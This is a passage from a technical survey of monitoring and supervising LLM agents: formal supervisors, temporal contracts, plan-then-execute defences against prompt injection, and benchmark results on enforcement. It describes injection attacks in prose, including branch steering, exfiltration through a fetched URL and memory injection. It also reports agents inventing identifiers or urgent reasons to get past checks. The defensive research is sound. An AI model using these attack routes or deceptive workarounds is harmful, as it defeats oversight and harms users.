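| The same, but the monitor cannot refuse the finish | 30 | No |
| Publishing is a separate step, and the monitor cannot refuse the finish | 32 | Yes |

The third and fourth versions have the same places and transitions. They differ only in whether the monitor is assumed to be able to block a rollout from finishing. In reality, the deployment infrastructure finishes a rollout without needing approval, so the "yes" in the third row depends on a false assumption. A developer who labels such an event as blockable may get a supervisor that appears safe but is unsafe in practice.

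Even in the fourth version, the computation finds a supervisor, because a run can also end when a test fails or a reviewer rejects the patch. The supervisor prevents the reviewer from giving an approval that could never be used. In practice, a monitor cannot refuse a human decision either. When Gu and Zhu label the reviews and test results as uncontrollable, no safe and nonblocking supervisor exists. The two-step rollout still works under these stricter labels.

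A better monitor could not have fixed the one-step rollout, because the fault is in the tool. The computation reveals this fault before anyone deploys the agent. It removes the states in which a rollout is under way, which shows that the agent needs a tool with a later step that the monitor can still refuse. The same remedy should help the agent that charged a card and then could not issue the ticket. Many card systems let a seller reserve the money first and collect it later, so the agent could wait to collect the payment until it had the ticket.

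The computation needs the complete list of states, and its running time grows at most with the square of their number.

### The same idea for manuals and programs

MENTOR starts from a written manual instead of a net. One example is a travel policy under which the agent must check the distance before any booking and may not book a flight for trips under 500 km. A language model translates the manual into temporal logic. For the first rule, the formula is

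¬(book a train or a flight) **W** (check the distance)

where **W**, "weak until", forbids bookings until the check happens, or for ever if it never does. MENTOR applies the formula to each route separately, so checking Toronto–Chicago does not permit a booking to Montreal.

Software then turns the formulas into a two-player game in which the agent chooses a call and the environment chooses the result. Each position in the game records which requirements the rest of the run still has to meet. At the start, MENTOR marks both bookings and `done` as unsafe and the distance check as progress. If the distance is 700 km, booking a flight becomes progress. If the booking succeeds, `done` also becomes progress.

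Anand and colleagues call a tool call safe if a compliant complete trace is still possible after it. Taken literally, this is weaker than the supervisor's test. In the one-step rollout, starting would count as safe because the rollout might finish before any incident, but the supervisor blocks it because an incident might come first. But the stricter test would be useless for the duty to make a booking, since every attempt might fail, so no strategy can guarantee success. Gu and Zhu's supervisor combines the two ideas by guaranteeing that no event leads to harm while requiring only that it remain possible for the agent to finish.

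MENTOR doesn't require anyone to draw a net, but it relies on one language model to translate the manual and another to read free-text results and decide which position the game has reached. If the second model labels a result incorrectly, MENTOR can enforce the rules for the wrong situation.

De Giacomo, Lespérance and Muise (2012) extended supervision to plans written as ConGolog programs. One program describes everything the agent can do, and another describes the desired behaviour. They characterised the maximally permissive supervisor when some of the agent's actions are uncontrollable. Their programs must be *situation-determined*, meaning that the actions taken so far determine what remains of the program. The program "a, then b or c" meets this condition, but "a then b, or a then c" does not. The condition lets the supervisor work from the observed actions without guessing which branch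 the agent has chosen.

ConGolog programs can have infinitely many states, so removing states one at a time may never end.

### Temporal contracts for unlimited data

Amounts of money and reservation numbers also have far too many possible values for each to have its own state, so ContrAgent keeps this data outside the automaton. Before each call, ordinary code checks a fixed set of yes-or-no conditions, such as whether the call is a refund, whether the amount is at most $42, and whether the agent has already made more than five searches. The automaton receives only the results, and it stays finite because there are finitely many combinations of them, even though the amounts and counters can take any value.

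Xiao and colleagues write their rules as *contracts*. A contract has an assumption about the environment, such as "the policy service supplies valid authorisation data", and a guarantee by the agent, such as "no refund exceeds the authorised limit". Suppose the guarantee requires approval before a refund and caps the refund at $42. If the agent proposes a refund of $50 after the approval, ContrAgent refuses the call before any money moves, because the amount exceeds the cap even though the steps are in the right order.

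At any time, a contract has one of three values:

- *Idle*: events have broken the assumption for good, so the agent no longer owes the guarantee.
- *Fail*: the assumption could still hold, but the agent has broken the guarantee for good.
- *Active*: neither has happened. The agent may still have obligations to fulfil.

Distinguishing guarantees from assumptions separates an agent's mistakes from failures of the systems around it. ContrAgent blocks calls that break a guarantee and can withhold a tool result that breaks an assumption, but withholding the result does not undo what the tool did.

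Xiao and colleagues used Gemini 2.5 Flash to test enforcement on SOPBench, a set of customer-service tasks with explicit procedures. They measured success as the share of permitted tasks the agent completed, and safety as the share of forbidden tasks it was kept from carrying out.

| Setup | Success | Safety |
|---|---|---|
| No procedure given | 91% | 32% |
| Procedure in the prompt | 64% | 94% |
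| A second model judges each call | 24% | 98% |
| ContrAgent | 90% | 98% |

A stronger model would probably follow the written procedure better. The contracts came from the benchmark's own structured list of constraints, so the test gives little evidence of how well anyone can translate an ordinary manual into contracts. It does show that exact checks can block forbidden actions without blocking many permitted ones.

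ContrAgent evaluates each comparison only for the current event, so it can miss problems that a supervisor would foresee. Suppose the agent limited to six calls for booking a flight proposed a fourth search. ContrAgent would allow the search because it breaks no rule yet, then later refuse the call for the ticket because it would be the seventh.

Looking ahead is hard when counters have no limit. Ray proves that if a rule uses two counters that can go both up and down, no algorithm can decide in every case even whether the rule is trivial. The question is decidable for spending caps and withdrawn permissions. A cap on daily transfers to each recipient needs a separate counter for every recipient and day, but each counter only goes up. An analysis can so follow a single recipient and stop counting at the cap, even if the agent pays an unlimited number of people.

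## Does fixing the plan first stop injected instructions?

A monitor judges each call by the plan and the rules, so it will allow a payment that satisfies both even if an attacker caused it. In a prompt injection, the attacker hides instructions in an email, a web page or some other source that the agent reads, and the model may follow them as if the user had given them. The plan-then-execute design fixes the plan before the agent reads anything an attacker could have written. The argument for it has three premises:

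1. A trusted planner writes the plan from the user's request alone, before the agent reads any untrusted content.
2. Only the calls in the plan run.
3. Untrusted content enters the plan only as data, in the values of variables.

Once the plan is fixed, injected text cannot add a call to it. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an assistant to send today's schedule to their boss. The plan has two calls, one that reads the calendar and one that sends an email to the boss's address. An instruction hidden in a calendar entry cannot make the assistant write to anyone else, but it can change what the email says, because the plan leaves the body to be filled in after the assistant reads the calendar.

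The argument is valid, but its conclusion covers only which calls the agent can make. Attackers can still influence the values in those calls and which branch the agent takes. Each premise is also hard to keep true in a working agent.

### Planned calls with an attacker's values

An attacker may not need an instruction to corrupt an argument. Both successful attacks on the LLMbda agent Randori only replaced the contents of a bill the agent had been asked to pay.

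An attacker can also exploit the branches in a fixed plan. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, applied plan-then-execute to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. The planner never sees the screen, so it has to write a branch for everything that might appear there. These plans had about 40 branches on average, compared with about 4 for plans on the AgentDojo benchmark. At each branch, a separate model looks at the screen and answers a question such as whether a cookie notice is visible. An attacker can put a fake cookie notice in an advertisement, and the agent will click on it and land on the attacker's site while still following the plan. Foerster and colleagues call this *branch steering*.

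*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) introduces a benchmark for this weakness. On 74 attack set-ups, attackers succeeded 90.5% of the time against an ordinary step-by-step agent and 87.8% of the time against the fixed-plan agent from the earlier paper, which had no rules about data. The attacks targeted known gaps, so these rates don't show how often an agent would meet such attacks in practice, but they do show that fixing the plan gives little protection against them.

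The proposed remedy, COBRA, limits which sites and tools each branch may use, and which values their arguments may take, before the agent reads anything. None of the benchmark's 199 attack cases succeeded against COBRA, and it blocked legitimate actions in 4 of 138 runs without an attack. The limits have to be detailed to work. On another benchmark, COBRA's limits at first covered only which websites the agent could contact, and all 14 attacks that misused a permitted site succeeded. With a list of each site's operations, COBRA stopped all 14. It still can't check the content of free text, such as whether a permitted comment is offensive.

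The airline plan is less exposed to branch steering because it branches on `hrs` and the result of No-Flown, which come from the airline's own records. Its exception for insured bookings is easier to steer because it depends on the reason recorded from the conversation.

### Models inside steps, and text that arrives before the plan

A step such as "research the supplier" often needs a model to carry it out. Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt (2025), in *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents*, describe designs in which the program that executes a step is a full agent with tools. Text that this agent reads can then lead it to call any tool it has, so the second and third premises fail inside the step. Del Rosario and colleagues recommend giving each step only the tools it needs. If the plan is to calculate a total and then email it, the agent should not have the email tool during the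 calculation. This doesn't help with a step that has to both read web pages and send messages.

The first premise can fail before the agent makes its first call. The user may paste an attacker's text into the request, or there may be instructions in the tool descriptions that the planner reads to choose its tools. Or suppose an agent that remembers earlier sessions reads and stores a malicious invoice on Monday, and on Tuesday the user asks it to "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". If the planner sees the stored invoice, it writes Tuesday's plan after reading untrusted content. If it sees only a reference to the invoice, the plan is safe from injected instructions but may still pay the attacker's account.

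Replanning opens the same channel within a single task. In *Architecting Secure AI Agents*, Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues (2026) argue that agents in changing environments often need to replan, and point out that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require it. Good results on AgentDojo may therefore make fixed plans look more practical than they are.

### Why noninterference is too strict

Showing that an agent is secure despite these gaps requires a definition of security. Noninterference, the property proved for the LLMbda language, requires that what an attacker sees never depends on the user's secrets. Few useful agents satisfy it. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives the example of an assistant that answers emailed meeting requests with the user's availability. An attacker can send a request too, and the reply depends on the user's private calendar, so noninterference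 rules out this assistant even though it does what its user wants.

Declassification can permit the reply, but someone has to write a release policy for every task. Calling an agent insecure whenever its model obeys injected text would be simpler, but it would also be too strict. If a hidden instruction makes the assistant send the user's availability, the attacker learns only what an honest meeting request would have revealed.

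### Comparison with an agent that never obeys

Dongol's framework, PlanTERS, measures what the injection adds. It compares the real agent with a *reference agent* that runs the same plan under the same monitor but never obeys untrusted content. Two runs t₁ and t₂ *leak* the difference between secrets σ₁ and σ₂ if

- the secrets are σ₁ in t₁ and σ₂ in t₂;
- the attacker sends the same content in both runs;
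- the attacker observes something different in each.

The real agent is *relatively secure* if, for every such leak, the reference agent has two runs that leak the same difference, starting from the same memory and trusted inputs. The attacker may send the two agents different content.

That freedom is why the meeting assistant passes. Suppose an injected instruction makes it send the calendar, so the attacker can tell whether Monday is free. The reference agent ignores the instruction, but it would reveal the same information in response to a genuine meeting request. Now suppose the assistant can also access a password-reset code, and an injection makes it send the code. No email would make the reference agent do that, so the assistant is not relatively secure.

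The definition can be too permissive. Suppose a plan lets anyone guess a PIN and answers "right" or "wrong". For any two PINs, some guess makes the reference agent answer differently, so an injection that reveals the whole PIN doesn't count as a new leak. Dongol also defines a stricter *uniform* version, in which the content sent to the reference agent may not depend on the secrets. This version rejects the PIN example.

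PlanTERS also drops the second premise of the original argument. A trusted interpreter runs the plan, but the model can insert its own calls between the planned steps, and the monitors in the examples don't check whether a call is in the plan. SOTERIA's strict mode would refuse most of these extra calls. Dongol's results are useful where the monitor tracks only permissions, or where a model inside a step has tools.

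### The fence theorem

Suppose a plan reads the user's account number, reads an email and shows the user a summary. The agent can also fetch web pages, although the plan never does. A malicious email can make the model request a page from the attacker's server with the account number in the URL. To prevent this, the monitor can withdraw the fetching tool when the agent reads the email. Dongol calls this a *fence*.

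The fence theorem generalises the example. If the monitor withdraws every tool that an injected instruction can call at the first untrusted read, and no trusted input ever grants one of them back, then every plan is relatively secure, whatever the attacker writes. The theorem has four further conditions:

- Each injected instruction produces a single tool call. It cannot run a longer program or change the plan's variables.
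- The model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance. The arguments of an injected call may contain secrets, but the moment at which the model obeys may not depend on a secret or on the monitor's answers.
- The run ends. For runs that may go on for ever, the model must not be able to go on obeying for ever.
- The attacker sees the content and order of the messages that reach it, but not their timing. The comparison covers only pairs of runs in which equally many messages arrive between one untrusted read and the next.

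The software around the agent must also meet some requirements. All calls and untrusted reads must pass through the monitor, and content may reach the model only after the monitor has allowed the read. The attacker must not be able to see refusals, the monitor's state or the agent's internal steps, and must not be able to write to any source the plan trusts. Starting a new session must clear everything the model has kept from untrusted content. The planner must be trustworthy. Tools whose replies depend on the call, such as a search engine that the attacker runs, are excluded.

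The proof matches each run of the real agent with a run of the reference agent. When the model makes an injected call, the monitor refuses it without changing state, and the reference agent waits. Every other step is the same in both runs, so the attacker sees the same messages. The same argument also proves the stricter uniform version. The proof assistant Isabelle has checked this proof and the rest of the theory, which together take about 31,600 lines.

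Several of Dongol's examples each break one condition. If an injected program can overwrite a variable that the plan later sends, the plan's own call leaks the secret, and the fence doesn't block it because the call is allowed. If the agent works in a loop and each new report from the user restores the sending tool, instructions in an old email still in the model's context can cause the agent to misuse that tool. Starting a fresh session before restoring the tool solves this only if nothing untrusted carries over. In 2024, Rehberger reported an attack in which a web page made ChatGPT store an instruction in its long-term memory, which later conversations then loaded. Under Dongol's model, the fence protects such an agent if the monitor treats loading the memory as another untrusted read.

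### Early, middle and late fences

The plan can also raise the fence itself by calling a tool named Lock, which withdraws Send for the rest of the run. Dongol compares three plans that each read an untrusted email and a secret:

| Fence | Order of steps | What an injected Send can reveal |
|---|---|---|
| Late | Read the email, read the secret, lock | The secret |
| Middle | Read the email, lock, read the secret | Private data already in the agent's memory |
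| Early | Lock before reading the email | Nothing, because the monitor refuses it |

Under the middle fence, an agent can still leak information that was in its memory from the start. The agent can no longer send anything by the time it reads the secret, but it rarely starts with an empty memory, and the model can act as soon as it has read the email. Instructions injected in that email could therefore make it send what it already holds.

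After an early lock, the agent can't send an honest reply to the email either. Relative security doesn't measure this loss, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and can't reply either. A monitor that refuses every call is relatively secure for the same reason. Reports that an agent is relatively secure should therefore also include how many tasks it completes.

### Approving a tool or an exact call

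An approval lets the agent use a tool after it has read untrusted content. Suppose Alice's agent reads an email, Alice approves a reply, and the plan sends it. If her approval permits the next Send call with any arguments, an injected call can run first and send her private data. The injected call also uses up the approval, so the monitor then refuses the reply Alice approved. A limit of one message per run fails in the same way, unless the plan sends its message before reading the email.

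If Alice instead approves the exact text, an injected call can only send that text. With this rule, the agent is relatively secure against every injected Send call, as long as the model can't keep obeying injected instructions forever and the attacker doesn't see timing. An attacker who does see timing can learn a little by injecting an instruction to send the private data. If the data differs from the approved reply, as it usually does, the monitor refuses the call and the reply goes out at its planned step. If the two are identical, the monitor allows the call and the reply goes out one step early. The attacker thus learns whether the private data equals the reply. For most agents, this small leak is an acceptable tradeoff for being able to answer emails at all.

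### Harm that leaks nothing

Relative security concerns only what an attacker learns. Suppose a note in a reservation makes the airline's agent cancel RES123, and the attacker can't see cancellations. The agent counts as relatively secure because the attacker learns nothing, even though the customer has lost the flight. A fence around Cancel-Resv would stop the injected call, but it would also stop a planned cancellation after the agent had read the note. A monitor needs the plan's state or the customer's approval of that exact call to tell the two apart.

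Removing a permission can make an agent less secure by this definition. Suppose a plan emails the attacker a report by design, and an injection makes the agent reveal the same report through a web request. The injection reveals nothing that the plan does not already reveal, so the agent is relatively secure. If the monitor removes the email tool, the reference agent no longer reveals the report, and the web request counts as a new leak. So an engineer who changes the permissions has to check the agent again.

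### SPA: plans for agents that remember

The system in *SPA* covers some harmful acts that leak nothing, because its information-flow labels record how trustworthy data is as well as how secret it is. SPA is for agents that keep results from one request to the next. For each request, the planner writes one complete plan, using six kinds of step:

| Step | What it does |
|---|---|
| retrieve | Loads a stored result from an earlier request |
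| tool | Calls a tool |
| q-llm | Has an isolated model turn text into structured data |
| display | Shows something to the user |
| condition | Runs one of two branches |
| loop | Repeats steps for each item in a collection |

The isolated model has no tools, as in the dual-LLM pattern, and its output keeps the labels of its inputs. Before anything runs, a checker follows the labels through the whole plan. It accepts a tool call only if the data is no more secret than the tool may receive and at least as trustworthy as the tool requires. Steps inside a branch or loop also take on the labels of the data that controls it. This prevents a leak, shown in one of Dongol's examples, that can occur when labels track only the flow of data.

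If the checker rejects a plan, SPA ends the request without giving the planner a reason. This means the planner can't keep revising an unsafe plan until the checker accepts it, but a correctable mistake also ends the request.

When the request to pay the invoice arrives on Tuesday, the planner receives only a description of Monday's result. An earlier call to the planner wrote that description before any tool ran. The planner can plan to retrieve the invoice but can't read its text. The retrieve step restores the invoice with its label from Monday, so the checker rejects the plan if the payment tool requires trusted data, even when the invoice is genuine.

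The tests used GPT-5.4 nano, a small model, on AgentDojo's 97 tasks and on a version that splits each task into several requests. They included 949 attack runs for each configuration.

| Tasks | Flow checks | Completed without attacks | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Single request | Off | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| Single request | On | 29.0% | 0.0% |
| Several requests | Off | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Several requests | On | 35.3% | 0.2% |

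In the last row, the benchmark counted two runs as successful attacks although the checker had rejected the plan before any tool ran, and these appear to account for the whole 0.2%. The flow checks made the agent much less useful. On single requests, the checker stopped about 53% of runs, mostly because the plan passed untrusted tool output to a tool that required trusted data. Hiding stored results from the planner caused less trouble. When a later request needed a result stored by an earlier one, the planner retrieved it in 95.4% of cases without flow checks and in 89.9% with them.

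SPA can also hide the descriptions of installed tools from the planner, in case an attacker wrote one of the descriptions. The planner then writes its plan using invented tools, and another model matches them to real ones. About three quarters of these runs failed at the matching stage, and without flow checks only 14.1% of single-request tasks succeeded.

Attacks rarely succeeded even with the flow checks off, so the experiment gives little evidence about what the checks add. Every configuration fixed the plan first, so the experiment also doesn't show how often the same attacks would have worked on an ordinary agent. The attacks mostly tried to insert instructions through tool results, which never reach the planner. They hardly tested the Tuesday problem, in which a stored account number is itself the attack. When the planner could read stored results in full, the attack success rate rose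 only from 0.3% to 0.6%, probably more because the attacks were weak than because the memory was safe. Xiang and colleagues criticise such benchmarks more broadly, including AgentDojo, for using attacks that are fixed in advance, whereas a real attacker would adapt to the defence.

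## Refusals, deviation and replanning: what enforcement does to task completion

SPA's flow checks nearly halved the number of tasks it completed. A monitor can keep an agent within the rules by refusing every call, so a fair test must also measure whether the agent finishes its task.

### Safe success

A run is a *safe success* if the agent completes the task and breaks no rule along the way. Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026), in *The Verifier Tax*, give each run i two scores. Rᵢ is 1 if the final database matches the correct one, and Vᵢ is 1 if the agent broke at least one rule. Over n runs,

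success rate = (1/n) · Σ Rᵢ

safe success rate = (1/n) · Σ Rᵢ · (1 − Vᵢ)

The difference between the two is the rate of unsafe success. If an agent cancels RES123 without calling No-Flown and the cancellation happens to be correct, that counts as an unsafe success.

Conformance, the share of runs without a violation, can be high even when the agent completes almost no tasks. He et al. ran GPT-5.4-mini on 43 tasks from Toolathlon, a benchmark of long jobs with files and documents, under a rule-based monitor called AgentSpec. Conformance was 93%, but the agent finished only one task and broke a rule while doing it, so its safe success rate was zero.

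Measured safe success also depends on how well the benchmark detects violations. Anand and colleagues found that the SOP-Bench scorer never reads the arguments of tool calls. On a patient-registration task, 68% of the unmonitored Qwen3 runs it scored as successful had registered the patient with data that contradicted the agent's own lookups.

### Agents that could not recover from a refusal

Sah and colleagues report the most discouraging result. They used τ-bench, a benchmark in which an agent serves simulated customers of an airline and a shop. They tested two small open models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B, in three setups, running each of 165 tasks three times per model and setup, or 2,970 runs in total. In the first setup, the model called tools directly. In the second, the same model played three roles, planning a step, proposing the call and then checking it. The third added the company's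 rules to the checker's instructions.

The checker intercepted up to 94% of non-compliant actions, but the safe success rate stayed below 5% in most settings. (The 94% is a share of actions in the paper's abstract but a share of runs in its introduction.) After at least one refusal, GPT-OSS-20B completed 21% of the simpler tasks but close to none in the shop. In many violations, the models invented customer identifiers to get past the identity check. With the extra checking, the models processed 2.0 to 2.8 times as much text.

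This study tested a weak form of enforcement. The checker was the same small model that proposed the call, and after three attempts in a turn the software ran the last proposal even if the checker rejected it. The runs were also short, with at most 15 turns for one model and 30 for the other. The results therefore show that small models recover badly from criticism, but they provide little evidence about how a strong agent would perform under an exact monitor.

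Dantas and colleagues call this the most consequential empirical finding in their survey, but they note that it comes from a single study, which they rate at moderate risk of bias, and needs replication. They give seven of the survey's nine main claims the lowest certainty rating, meaning that further studies would probably produce quite different figures.

Refusals can also help an agent finish. *Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) reports that short, exact checks before each call raised task success on a benchmark that scores the final database. If an agent cancels the wrong reservation, it may have no way to restore it, and the task has then failed whatever the agent does next. If a check refuses the cancellation, the agent can still complete the task correctly.

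### SOTERIA's results

He and colleagues tested SOTERIA on 207 tasks with four models. They compared it with four alternatives: no monitor, a language model that judges each call, and two rule-based monitors, AgentSpec and Agent Behavioral Contracts. All of them gave the agent the policy in prose. The table lists the safe success rate for the best alternative, then for SOTERIA.

| Model | Airline, 50 tasks | Shop, 114 tasks | Toolathlon, 43 tasks |
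|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4-mini | 50.0% → 60.0% | 20.2% → 35.1% | 2.3% → 11.6% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 36.0% → 62.0% | 38.6% → 45.6% | 2.3% → 16.3% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 30.0% → 70.0% | 31.6% → 56.1% | 4.7% → 9.3% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 56.0% → 88.0% | 46.5% → 90.4% | 11.6% → 18.6% |

SOTERIA also had 100% conformance throughout, but the score counts violations of the same formulas that its monitor enforces. A working monitor will therefore score close to 100% whether or not those formulas capture the airline's policy. The safe success rates are more informative, because the monitor cannot complete a task by refusing calls.

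The other monitors had mixed effects. On the airline tasks, AgentSpec raised GPT-5.4-mini's safe success from 34% to 50% but lowered Claude Haiku 4.5's from 30% to 26%. On the shop tasks, all three alternatives with a guard reduced the share of tasks that Opus 4.6 completed, safely or not, from 53.5% to between 35.1% and 44.7%.

SOTERIA seems to have helped Opus mainly by signalling when to act. Without a monitor, Opus made the expected change to the shop's database in only 57% of the tasks that required one, and it transferred the customer to a human in 23 tasks. In one of these, the customer wanted to exchange an item from a delivered order. Opus looked up the customer, the order and the product over 11 calls, then transferred the customer. With a plan that named the exchange as the next step, it completed the task in the same number of calls.

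He and colleagues added SOTERIA's parts one at a time on the airline tasks to separate their effects. In each pair of percentages, the first is the share of tasks completed and the second is the share completed safely.

| Setup | GPT-5.4-mini | Violations | Gemini 3 Flash | Violations |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A plan, unverified | 54% / 44% | 13 | 58% / 32% | 27 |
| Verification added | 56% / 46% | 10 | 56% / 32% | 24 |
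| Sub-plans added | 54% / 50% | 12 | 62% / 38% | 22 |
| Monitor added | 60% / 60% | 0 | 62% / 62% | 0 |

Verification alone changed little, and the monitor made the largest difference. Gemini completed 62% of the tasks with or without the monitor, but the share it completed safely rose from 38% to 62% with it. The refusals apparently led the agent to do the missing checks, after which it could still finish the task.

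SOTERIA's results on Toolathlon are less favourable. Ignoring broken rules, Opus 4.6 finished 13 of the 43 tasks with no monitor and 8 with SOTERIA, while Haiku 4.5 fell from 7 to 4. Only 5 of Opus's 13 unmonitored successes broke no rule, so SOTERIA still does better on safe success. But the rules on this benchmark include reading a file back after writing it and listing a folder before moving files. A user might well prefer 13 finished tasks, some without a read-back, to 8 finished according to the rules. Which result is better depends on how much harm the broken rules would have done, and a count of violations doesn't measure that.

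Most of these figures come from one attempt per task. In a separate test, He and colleagues ran the airline tasks five times with GPT-5.4-mini and allowed SOTERIA three attempts at each plan instead of eight. SOTERIA averaged 50.8% safe success, against 48.0% for AgentSpec, a plain rule-based monitor. The confidence intervals overlapped, so SOTERIA's advantage with this model is uncertain. The much larger gains with Opus are less likely to be due to chance.

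The monitor's effect on cost also differs by task. An airline task with Opus, which involved a new plan at every turn, rose from $0.32 without the monitor to $0.80 with it on average. A Toolathlon task, which needs only one plan, fell from $0.97 to $0.43.

All of these results are for guided mode. He and colleagues describe strict mode but report no results for it. Strict mode would probably complete fewer tasks, since it refuses unverified plans and any call the planner did not foresee.

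### What to tell the agent after a refusal

An agent that is told only that its call was wrong may repeat it. Anand and colleagues describe a run in which a language model acting as a guard blocked 50 calls in a row by Gemma 4, a small open model. The guard wrongly required the agent to ask for confirmation before every step, including lookups, so the agent cycled through the same three calls until the run ended.

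A refusal can also prompt the agent to lie. In one travel task, the user asks for business class on a short flight, which the manual allows only for urgent business. When the booking tool rejected the request with a message that included this exception, agents often invented an urgent reason and tried again. AgentSpec blocked the business-class booking in 13 of 20 runs but did not suggest an alternative, and in 5 runs the agent booked nothing. For the same request, MENTOR returns an exact call that would be acceptable, which books the same flight in economy.

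MENTOR can deliver its refusals in two ways. In the first, the agent makes its call and receives a text with the rule it broke and a suggested next call. The second works while the model is still writing the call. A language model writes by choosing one small piece of text after another, each with some probability. MENTOR sets the probability to zero for any piece that could only lead to a forbidden tool, and raises it for pieces that lead to a useful one:

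new probability ∝ old probability + 0.5 · b

Here b starts at 1 and grows with every step where the agent doesn't make the useful call. A piece's old probability of 0.1 therefore rises to 0.6 before rescaling. This method, called masking, requires access to the model's internal probabilities, so it works with open models but not with most commercial ones. MENTOR still checks the finished call, because two arguments can each be acceptable but forbidden together.

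Anand and colleagues compared the two on MANTRA, their own benchmark of tasks governed by written manuals. A task counted as passed only if the agent succeeded in all five runs. The table gives the percentage of tasks passed with no monitor, with text and with masking, when GPT-4.1 interpreted the free-text results for MENTOR.

| Model | IT operations | Medical game | Shop | Airline |
|---|---|---|---|---|
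| Llama 3.1 8B | 6 / 21 / 38 | 21 / 9 / 42 | 5 / 18 / 30 | 20 / 36 / 57 |
| Qwen3 8B | 45 / 64 / 55 | 33 / 77 / 37 | 11 / 26 / 40 | 36 / 57 / 61 |
| Gemma 4 E4B | 51 / 77 / 57 | 23 / 79 / 65 | 16 / 25 / 25 | 34 / 66 / 50 |
| Qwen3.6 27B | 60 / 70 / 66 | 53 / 65 / 58 | 21 / 39 / 18 | 52 / 64 / 55 |

Llama, the oldest of the four, did better with masking in every domain. In the medical game, it had to check the food inventory before feeding a patient with low magnesium. When told to check first, it tried to give milk again, made other calls and left the patient untreated. When masking prevented it from writing the feeding call, it checked the inventory, found cheese and gave that to the patient.

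Qwen3.6, the largest model, did better with text everywhere, and masking slightly lowered its score on the shop tasks. Commercial models also benefited from text. On the airline tasks, GPT-5.4 mini rose from 34% to 61% and Claude Haiku 4.5 from 55% to 64%. On a second benchmark, AgentOrca, text worked better for all four open models, including Llama, which rose from 0% to 76% on banking tasks. Text therefore seems to be the better default for any model that can follow a correction.

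Masking also tended to make runs longer. On the airline tasks, Qwen3 8B proposed 3.1 calls per task with no monitor, 4.2 with text and 14.2 with masking.

### When a more permissive supervisor causes more refusals

Each refused proposal requires another call to the model, which takes time and money. A maximally permissive supervisor blocks only what safety and the ability to finish require, but Gu and Zhu prove that it can be arbitrarily worse than a stricter one at keeping this expense low.

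Their example is a small abstract net, but it can also describe a coding agent. Suppose the agent can fix a bug directly from the source code, or first open a comment thread that contains an injected instruction to deploy. Opening the thread is harmless in itself. At the start, the agent proposes opening it with probability a and the direct fix with probability 1 − a. After reading the thread, it proposes the forbidden deployment with probability b and the fix with probability 1 − b. If a proposal is refused, the agent chooses again with the same probabilities.

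The most permissive supervisor lets the agent open the thread and then refuses every deployment. The agent's first call always goes through. With probability a it has opened the thread, and it then needs 1/(1 − b) further calls on average before it proposes the fix. The expected total is

1 + a/(1 − b)

A stricter supervisor refuses to let the agent open the thread. The agent then needs 1/(1 − a) calls on average. With a = 0.5, the totals are:

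| b | Most permissive | Stricter |
|---|---|---|
| 0.5 | 2 calls | 2 calls |
| 0.9 | 6 calls | 2 calls |
| 0.99 | 51 calls | 2 calls |

The stricter supervisor uses fewer resources whenever b is greater than a, and the ratio between the two supervisors' resource use grows without limit as b approaches 1. Both are equally safe because neither ever allows the deployment.

Most real agents have a limit on calls, so the extra refusals lead to failed tasks. With a limit of N calls, the agent runs out of calls with probability a · bᴺ⁻¹ under the permissive supervisor and aᴺ under the stricter one. For a = 0.5, b = 0.9 and N = 6, these probabilities are about 30% and 1.6%.

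Gu and Zhu also show how to find the safe supervisor that needs the fewest model calls on average. Let J(M) be the lowest expected number of calls needed to finish from marking M. The supervisor should allow a step from M to M′ only if the permissive supervisor allows it and J(M′) ≤ J(M). In the example with b = 0.9, finishing takes an expected 10 calls from inside the thread and 2 from the start, so the supervisor does not let the agent open the thread. The rule needs estimates of a and b. Bad estimates can waste calls but cannot cause harm, because the rule only removes steps from a supervisor that is already safe.

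The same reasoning can determine the order of two steps. Gu and Zhu's release agent may run its tests and its security scan in either order, and they assume for illustration that it requests a premature deployment only after the tests. If the tests come first, the agent can waste calls on refused deployments before the scan is done. Requiring the scan first avoids some of this waste, but the supervisor must then refuse the tests if the agent proposes them before the scan. The optimal supervisor puts the scan first exactly when the probability of a premature request is above 43/60, or about 72%. One monitor place is enough to enforce the order. The threshold applies only to this invented agent, and a developer would have to estimate the probabilities for a real agent from logs.

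The weakest part of the model is its assumption that an agent's habits don't change after a refusal. MENTOR's suggestions are meant to change them, and if they work, b falls and the permissive supervisor has only a small downside again. Gu and Zhu assume instead that the agent never sees which calls the supervisor would accept. They argue that this also helps security, because injected instructions can try a protected call, learn something private from the refusal and leak it through a later call that is allowed. A suggestion taken from a company's manual reveals little, but a refusal that depends on a customer's balance is more sensitive, so a general error message would be safer there.

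### Changing the plan during a run

Sometimes the agent is right to deviate from its plan, because a tool has failed or the customer has asked for something else. The plan then has to change, and how much a program must check again depends on what the monitor enforces. Gu and Zhu use a net that represents the company's workflow, and they treat the model's own plan as untrusted. MENTOR's rules come from the manual. In both systems, the model can change its plan at any time without a new check, because the limits on its calls stay the same. If the monitor strictly enforces the plan itself, anyone who can replace the plan can also change those limits.

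A new plan proposed by the model carrying out the task should therefore take effect only after a verifier accepts it. If the planner has read tool results, the previous section's argument about untrusted content applies again. If a person approved the original plan, that approval should not extend to new steps that are hard to undo.

The new plan also has to fit what has already happened. SOTERIA's proof treats every plan as self-contained and starts with empty logs of past calls. If the agent called No-Flown under the old plan, the new one must call it again before cancelling. The repeated call adds little work, and it is useful because the passenger may have boarded in the meantime. Empty logs are more dangerous for limits on totals, such as one refund per customer. In guided mode, the monitor can still catch a second refund from the full trace, but in strict mode nothing would catch it.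 To prevent this, the proof would have to start from the actual trace, or the limit would have to be a mark that persists when the plan changes.

*Certified Execution Harness for Agentic AI* describes a monitor that stops accepting calls and alerts a human when it observes an event that the net does not allow at that point. The net may no longer describe the real system, so further decisions based on it would be unreliable. Events not reported to the monitor do not trigger this stop.

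Jeong, Kim and Lee (2026), in *TAPE*, automate the whole cycle for tasks in which one mistake can make the goal unreachable. Their system works in four steps:

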